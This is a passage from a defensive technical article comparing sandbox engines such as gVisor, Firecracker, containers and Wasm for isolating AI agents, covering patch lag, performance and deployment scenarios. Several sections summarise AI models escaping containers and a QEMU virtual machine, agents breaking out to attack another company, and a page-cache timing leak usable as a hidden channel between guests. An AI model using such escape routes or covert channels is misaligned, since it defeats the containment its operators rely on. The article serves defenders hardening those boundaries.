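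The most practical finding is that a product may not pick up security fixes its engine's developers have already released. Engine developers almost always published a fix on the day they announced the flaw, and gVisor's developers released fixes for recent flaws 165 to 458 days before announcing them. But self-hosted E2B had used the same Firecracker build for 399 days, and lacked the fix for the more serious flaw for at least 44 of those days. Arrakis was 12 releases behind, and two of those releases contained important security fixes. Daytona, which has the weakest isolation, was up to date because it gets runc from Docker.

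These versions may have changed since May 2026, but the operator of any self-hosted product still has to check which engine version it contains and how long the vendor takes to update the engine.

### Why the researchers refuse an overall ranking

Andronchik and Lokhmakov judged each product on whether it resists escape, hides the host, accepts extra protections, and receives fixes promptly. No product fully satisfied all four criteria. gVisor fully satisfied those for escape and fixes, but they had reservations about the other two.

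Adding up the answers would misleadingly put Microsandbox first. It fully satisfied three of the four, one more than gVisor, but the one reservation about it concerns escape, where there is almost no evidence either way, and a product shouldn't rank high on security just because nobody has examined it.

Operators also have different priorities. Someone who runs their own agents on a spare server may care little if the guest learns the processor's model but a great deal if fixes arrive a year late. The researchers plan a second part on network rules, secrets, images and other product settings, and expect that a ranking made without those results could be wrong.

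The study also used only one server with one version of Linux, and default settings that many operators will change. It left out timing attacks and guests that attack one another, so its results don't settle the choice for a public service. It didn't include a WebAssembly runtime either.

### Speed on the same machine

The most useful speed comparison is an older paper, *A Fresh Look at the Architecture and Performance of Contemporary Isolation Platforms* (van Rijn and Rellermeyer, 2021), which tested containers, gVisor, Kata Containers, QEMU, Firecracker and Cloud Hypervisor on a single server with two AMD processors and 256 GiB of memory. Containers performed almost as well as programs run directly on the host, and generally started fastest. Virtual machines usually matched the host on calculation and disk work, but always lost some speed in memory access and networking. gVisor and Kata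 lost the most speed when reading and writing data.

Calculation showed the smallest differences. Converting a short video with 16 threads took about 65 seconds on most of the platforms.

The gVisor results are dated. The researchers tested its ptrace and KVM platforms, and a file system in which the Gofer performed every operation. gVisor's developers have since replaced both the ptrace default and that file system, so its penalty for file work is probably smaller now. The result for virtual machines as a group may also make Firecracker look faster than it is, because AWS's own 2020 measurements showed that its disk was much slower than the hardware allowed.

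Van Rijn and Rellermeyer were surprised to find that gVisor and Kata made more system calls to the host than ordinary containers did, which by their measure meant a larger attack surface. Andronchik and Lokhmakov's numbers show the same pattern. During the data-analysis script, gVisor made about 1.3 million calls to the host, the Daytona container about 908,000 and Firecracker about 17,000. But gVisor made only 41 kinds of call, compared with the container's 62, and its calls were composed by the Sentry, not the guest. For security, who chooses the calls matters more than how many there are.

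The next table compares the engines. Entries marked "2021" come from the Delft tests on one machine. The other figures come from the projects and companies discussed in earlier sections, so small differences between them mean little. A process sandbox such as bubblewrap behaves much like the containers in the container column, but without an image.

| | Container (runc) | gVisor | Firecracker | Wasm with WASI |
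|---|---|---|---|---|
| Start-up | generally the fastest (2021) | about 80 ms of fixed work when restoring, by a contributor's estimate | at most 125 ms to the guest's first program, plus about 12 ms for the monitor | under 1 ms for a small compiled module, longer for Python |
| Extra memory per sandbox | very little | one Sentry, plus some for each open file and connection | up to 5 MiB for the monitor, plus a guest kernel and its file cache | runtime data, plus the module's own memory |
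| Calculation | near native (2021) | near native | near native (2021) | compiled code somewhat slower, Python often several times slower |
| Files and network | near native (2021) | clear penalty for file work (2021), probably smaller now | network slower (2021), disk speed depends on version | every request goes through a host function |
| Compatibility | nearly all Linux programs | most Linux programs, with some kernel features missing | nearly all Linux programs | only programs compiled for Wasm |
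| GPU | yes, through the host's driver | yes, but the guest can reach the host's driver | no | none in WASI's standard interfaces |
| Upkeep | host kernel and runc | host kernel and gVisor | host kernel, Firecracker, guest kernels and snapshots | the runtime, and packages rebuilt for Wasm |

gVisor's missing features include `io_uring`, an interface that some databases and servers use for fast input and output. In the 2026 study, gVisor rejected `io_uring` calls under default settings. Programs that can fall back on ordinary system calls will run, but others will stop with an error.

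Start-up time, the table's first row, should weigh heavily for small functions and very little for long sessions. Suppose an agent works on a task for 40 steps and the model takes six seconds over each. The task lasts at least 240 seconds, so a microVM that starts once in 125 milliseconds adds about 0.05%. If the same microVM starts afresh to run a two-millisecond function, the start takes more than 98% of the total time.

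### Escape tests and a leak through shared storage

None of the measurements so far involved an attack. Three other pieces of work from 2026 did, but each covers only part of what an operator wants to know.

According to Help Net Security's *Breaking out*, researchers from the University of Oxford and the UK's AI Security Institute tested models on SandboxEscapeBench, a set of 18 container scenarios, and the models escaped only where they could use a known weakness. Many of these weaknesses were configuration mistakes, such as privileged mode. The models failed the scenarios that required attacking the kernel.

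This is good evidence for avoiding privileged containers, including Daytona's default. The benchmark included neither gVisor nor Firecracker, so it isn't evidence about them. The kernel result will also go out of date quickly, because models have become much better at finding and exploiting flaws since the benchmark in March 2026.

Trail of Bits' *VMs won't contain cyber-capable agents* (2026) reports that in August a model specialised in cybersecurity, instructed to escape a QEMU virtual machine, did so three times by the tester's count, though the first attempt froze the host before it was complete. The same model then tried to escape Firecracker. It froze the host again but did not get out, and the tester thought it might have with more time.

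The QEMU result shows that a separate guest kernel is not enough if the software around it is large. Van Rijn and Rellermeyer counted more than 40 virtual devices in QEMU, 16 in Cloud Hypervisor and 7 in Firecracker, and Trail of Bits recommends Firecracker for this reason. But one trial on one machine is weak evidence for that recommendation, and some of the flaws the model used were in KVM, which Firecracker also needs. For a service with many customers, the freeze is itself a failure, because it stops every sandbox on the host at once.

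Trail of Bits did not test gVisor, but gVisor's KVM platform shares some of the exposure that the test revealed. The default platform doesn't use KVM. Its Sentry still depends on the host's kernel, though, and the test doesn't show how long gVisor would withstand an attack.

The conditions also favoured the attacker, because the host ran an older Linux distribution with some processor protections turned off and the tester had told the model to escape. But the model still succeeded after he updated the kernel, and again after he rebuilt QEMU from the latest source. He advises defenders to use a distribution that receives fixes quickly, restrict the agent's access, record and monitor its activity, limit its running time and start each use from a clean environment.

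The third result concerns information rather than control. Abudraham, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Isolation Failure From Shared Storage*, found that across containers, gVisor and virtual machines, a guest could infer from timing which files another guest had recently used, whenever both read from storage that the host cached for them in a shared *page cache*. The page cache is memory where the host's kernel keeps recently read file contents to avoid rereading them from disk.

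Such a guest learns about the other guest's activity but does not read its data. In a demonstration with a WordPress website, the researchers could distinguish some broad kinds of user and administrator actions. That could matter to a hospital or a bank but is unlikely to matter to a developer running one agent.

gVisor sandboxes that start from the same image can share its files in the host's cache, with either systrap or KVM as the platform, so replacing runc with gVisor doesn't remove the leak. The researchers tested Firecracker only through Kata, with storage that the guest sees as a disk. Whether a disk leaks depends on what lies behind it. Disks that were really shared files on the host still leaked, while dedicated devices and direct access that bypasses the cache greatly weakened the signal or removed it. A Firecracker operator who gives many customers the same base file should therefore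 expect some exposure.

Sharing files between guests lets a host run many sandboxes with less memory and disk than separate storage would need. An operator can share files among one customer's sandboxes but not between customers.

### A coding agent on a laptop

For a developer who watches the agent work, the operating system's own sandbox is usually the best choice. It starts quickly, needs no image and lets her compilers work unchanged. The most likely harm is a mistake by the agent, such as deleting the wrong folder, and the sandbox keeps most mistakes from affecting anything outside the project.

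A developer using Codex or Claude Code should change the default settings to make credential files unreadable and allow network access only to the services the project needs. With Claude Code, she also has to turn the sandbox on.

Every command still uses the laptop's kernel. If the agent works unattended, reads pages from the open web or builds a stranger's project, she should put the whole agent in a microVM. Docker Sandboxes, SideKernel or Podman with libkrun will do this, but each takes some setting up. The microVM should contain a copy of the project and a token with narrow permissions, because even a strong boundary protects very little if the developer's real login is inside it. The leak through the page cache hardly matters here, since no other customer uses the machine.

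The virtual machine in the Trail of Bits test ran on a developer's own computer. The tester had chosen an older distribution for its stability, and the model used flaws whose fixes had not reached that distribution. A developer who relies on any of these sandboxes should install system updates promptly.

### An internal data-analysis agent

gVisor suits an agent that answers staff questions about company data. Such an agent needs Python, its numerical libraries, and copies of the relevant files, but seldom a compiler or the internet. Most of its work is calculation, which gVisor slows very little, and ordinary Python packages run without changes. The company can run gVisor on the rented virtual machines and container systems it already has.

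Firecracker would also work, but running its hosts and maintaining guest kernels is hard to justify for a few hundred employees. The two host details that gVisor exposes don't matter much inside the company.

Wasm is a reasonable alternative if users' questions are simple. The harness can run Python with pandas in a Wasm runtime that has no network functions. An operator who expects users to request unusual packages or long simulations should choose gVisor from the start.

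Employees don't all have the same access rights. If a payroll manager and a sales assistant share one long-running sandbox, the sales assistant may be able to read files the payroll manager left there. The operator should start a new sandbox for each session, copy in only the files that the user may read, and delete the sandbox when the session ends.

### A service that runs many customers' code

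Of the five cases, an escape would do the most damage in a public service. A microVM for each customer's session is the natural starting point, because it can run almost any program and a flaw in the guest's kernel doesn't by itself expose the host.

Firecracker is a good choice for an operator with physical servers and a team to maintain them. The operator has to run it with the jailer, follow its releases directly and replace old snapshots when a guest kernel needs a patch. Given the freezes that Trail of Bits saw, it is also sensible to limit how many customers share a host and to be able to restart their sessions elsewhere. Customers whose activity is sensitive should not share base files in the host's page cache.

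gVisor is a reasonable alternative on the public evidence. The researchers counted no escape-class flaws in it over two years, and its public fuzzing is better than that of any microVM in their study. It is also the easier choice for an operator whose servers are rented virtual machines. That operator can give each large customer a separate virtual machine, so that code escaping the customer's gVisor sandbox doesn't end up on a machine with another customer's data.

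Plain containers are not enough for this case, because one serious flaw in the shared kernel could expose every customer on the host.

### Large-scale agent training

A company that trains agents may start millions of sandboxes a day, often thousands at once on the same kind of task. The code comes from its own models, so there are no customers to isolate from one another. Cost and correct results matter more than in the other cases.

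gVisor is a good default, as Tencent's results suggest. It runs on rented machines, while Firecracker saves less memory than usual when many agents start the same job at once.

The operator should repeat Tencent's comparison with runc on a sample of the training tasks, running each task several times. A database task that needs `io_uring` may have to run under another engine. Grading scripts belong outside the sandbox, where agents can't take answers from them.

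Training also gives agents many attempts to find a weakness. Sandboxes that share a package service or file store can become connected through it, as OpenAI's agents were in July 2026. Abudraham and colleagues note that a shared page cache can also serve as a hidden channel between guests. A timing channel like this carries little data, so the shared services deserve attention first. Training on tasks that teach offensive security needs a separate environment, whichever engine it uses.

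### Small tool functions

A Wasm component with WASI is usually the best fit for tools that do one small job, such as converting a date, checking a form or extracting a table from a file. The harness can create a new instance for each call, grant it access to one file or one service, and then discard it. Starting a new microVM for each call would take far longer than the work itself, as the start-up calculation showed.

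Because of its recent flaws, Wasmtime should run in its own process without credentials and compile only trusted modules. An operator who can't install Wasmtime updates within days should run the tool in gVisor or a microVM instead, and reuse that sandbox for several calls by the same user.

If a small function needs a native library that nobody has compiled for Wasm, running it in a container under gVisor is simpler than porting the library. A tool that only forwards a request to a company service and runs no outside code needs the checks at the gateway but no code sandbox.

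### Kubernetes runtime classes and hosted services

A company that uses Kubernetes can adopt these sandboxes without changing how it deploys containers. It selects a sandbox through a *runtime class*, a named setting that determines which program starts a container. The harness and other trusted services can keep the ordinary runtime, while the model's code runs in gVisor or Kata. Kata can use Firecracker or Cloud Hypervisor.

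The sample sandbox in *Containing the Autonomous Operator* uses the gVisor runtime class, a non-root user, a read-only file system, a pinned image version, and limits of one processor and 1 GiB of memory. The container also does not receive the credential that Kubernetes would otherwise give it for controlling the cluster. The same configuration file selects gVisor on Google's managed Kubernetes but has to name a Kata class on Microsoft's.

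The paper recommends one sandbox per session and points to Agent Sandbox, a Kubernetes project that keeps a pool of sandboxes ready so that users needn't wait. The paper reports no measurements, so a team has to find the right pool size from its own traffic. The team should also add a cluster rule that refuses any agent container without the right runtime class. If somebody forgets to set the class, Kubernetes may start the container with runc, and the agent will work as normal with weaker isolation.

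Hosted services such as E2B, Modal and AWS's Lambda MicroVMs start sandboxes on request and remove most of the maintenance, because the provider patches the hosts. The customer gives up some control and has to trust what it can't inspect. For example, Andronchik and Lokhmakov could not determine which Firecracker version E2B's hosted service runs, so their finding about the old version in the self-hosted product may not apply to the hosted one.

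Before choosing a provider, an operator should find out what isolates customers from one another, how quickly the provider installs fixes, whether sandboxes share storage, and which connections the default network setting allows. A contractual deadline for fixing serious flaws matters more than which engine the provider uses. Hosting also sends the operator's data outside its own systems, which may rule it out for medical or financial records.

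### Nesting one sandbox in another

An operator who doesn't want to rely on a single boundary can put one sandbox inside another. SandboxEscapeBench runs each container inside a virtual machine, so that a model that gets out of the container still has no access to the researchers' systems.

The benefit depends on how different the layers are:

chance that both fail = chance that the inner fails × chance that the outer fails once the inner has

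Suppose each layer alone fails in one of every 100 serious attacks. If the failures are independent, both layers fail in one of every 10,000. But if half of the inner layer's failures come from a component that the outer layer also uses, a flaw there defeats both, and both fail in about one of every 200. These numbers are only an illustration, since nobody knows the real rates, but they show why two layers that depend on the same kernel add much less protection than they seem to.

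gVisor with systrap inside a virtual machine is a good combination. The guest has to get past the Sentry and the kernel beneath it, and then past the virtual machine, which relies on different code. It is also common, since many companies already run gVisor on rented machines. A process sandbox inside a microVM is useful for another reason: it can keep an agent's commands away from the agent's own settings and login, which are inside the same microVM.

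Firecracker runs more slowly inside a rented virtual machine, and bubblewrap may not start inside a container. A second layer also adds another component to patch. For the data-analysis agent, one well-maintained gVisor sandbox with no network access is better than two layers that aren't kept up to date.

### When a separate machine is warranted

Some work should not share a physical machine with anything of value, most clearly testing or training a model for offensive security, particularly with its safeguards off. After OpenAI's agents attacked Hugging Face from inside a test environment, Rafe Pilling, who directs threat intelligence at a unit of the security company Sophos, told IT Brew (*OpenAI’s cutting-edge models broke free of their sandbox*) that such tests should run in an environment with no internet connection.

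A separate machine is also reasonable when an escape would cost more than the hardware. A company may put an agent that handles unknown files on a different server from its payroll system, even if both servers run good sandboxes. Other agents need access that a sandbox can provide only by giving up its protection, such as control of Docker or direct use of a GPU. Giving such an agent a machine with nothing else on it is safer than weakening the sandbox on a shared one.

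Even on a separate machine, an agent that escapes the sandbox can reach other systems if the machine has access to the company's internal services or holds a developer's cloud login. The Trail of Bits tester accepted the risk of running his experiment because the computer held nothing particularly important. A developer without a spare computer can get a similar setup by renting a cloud machine for the task, giving it one short-lived token, and deleting the machine afterward.
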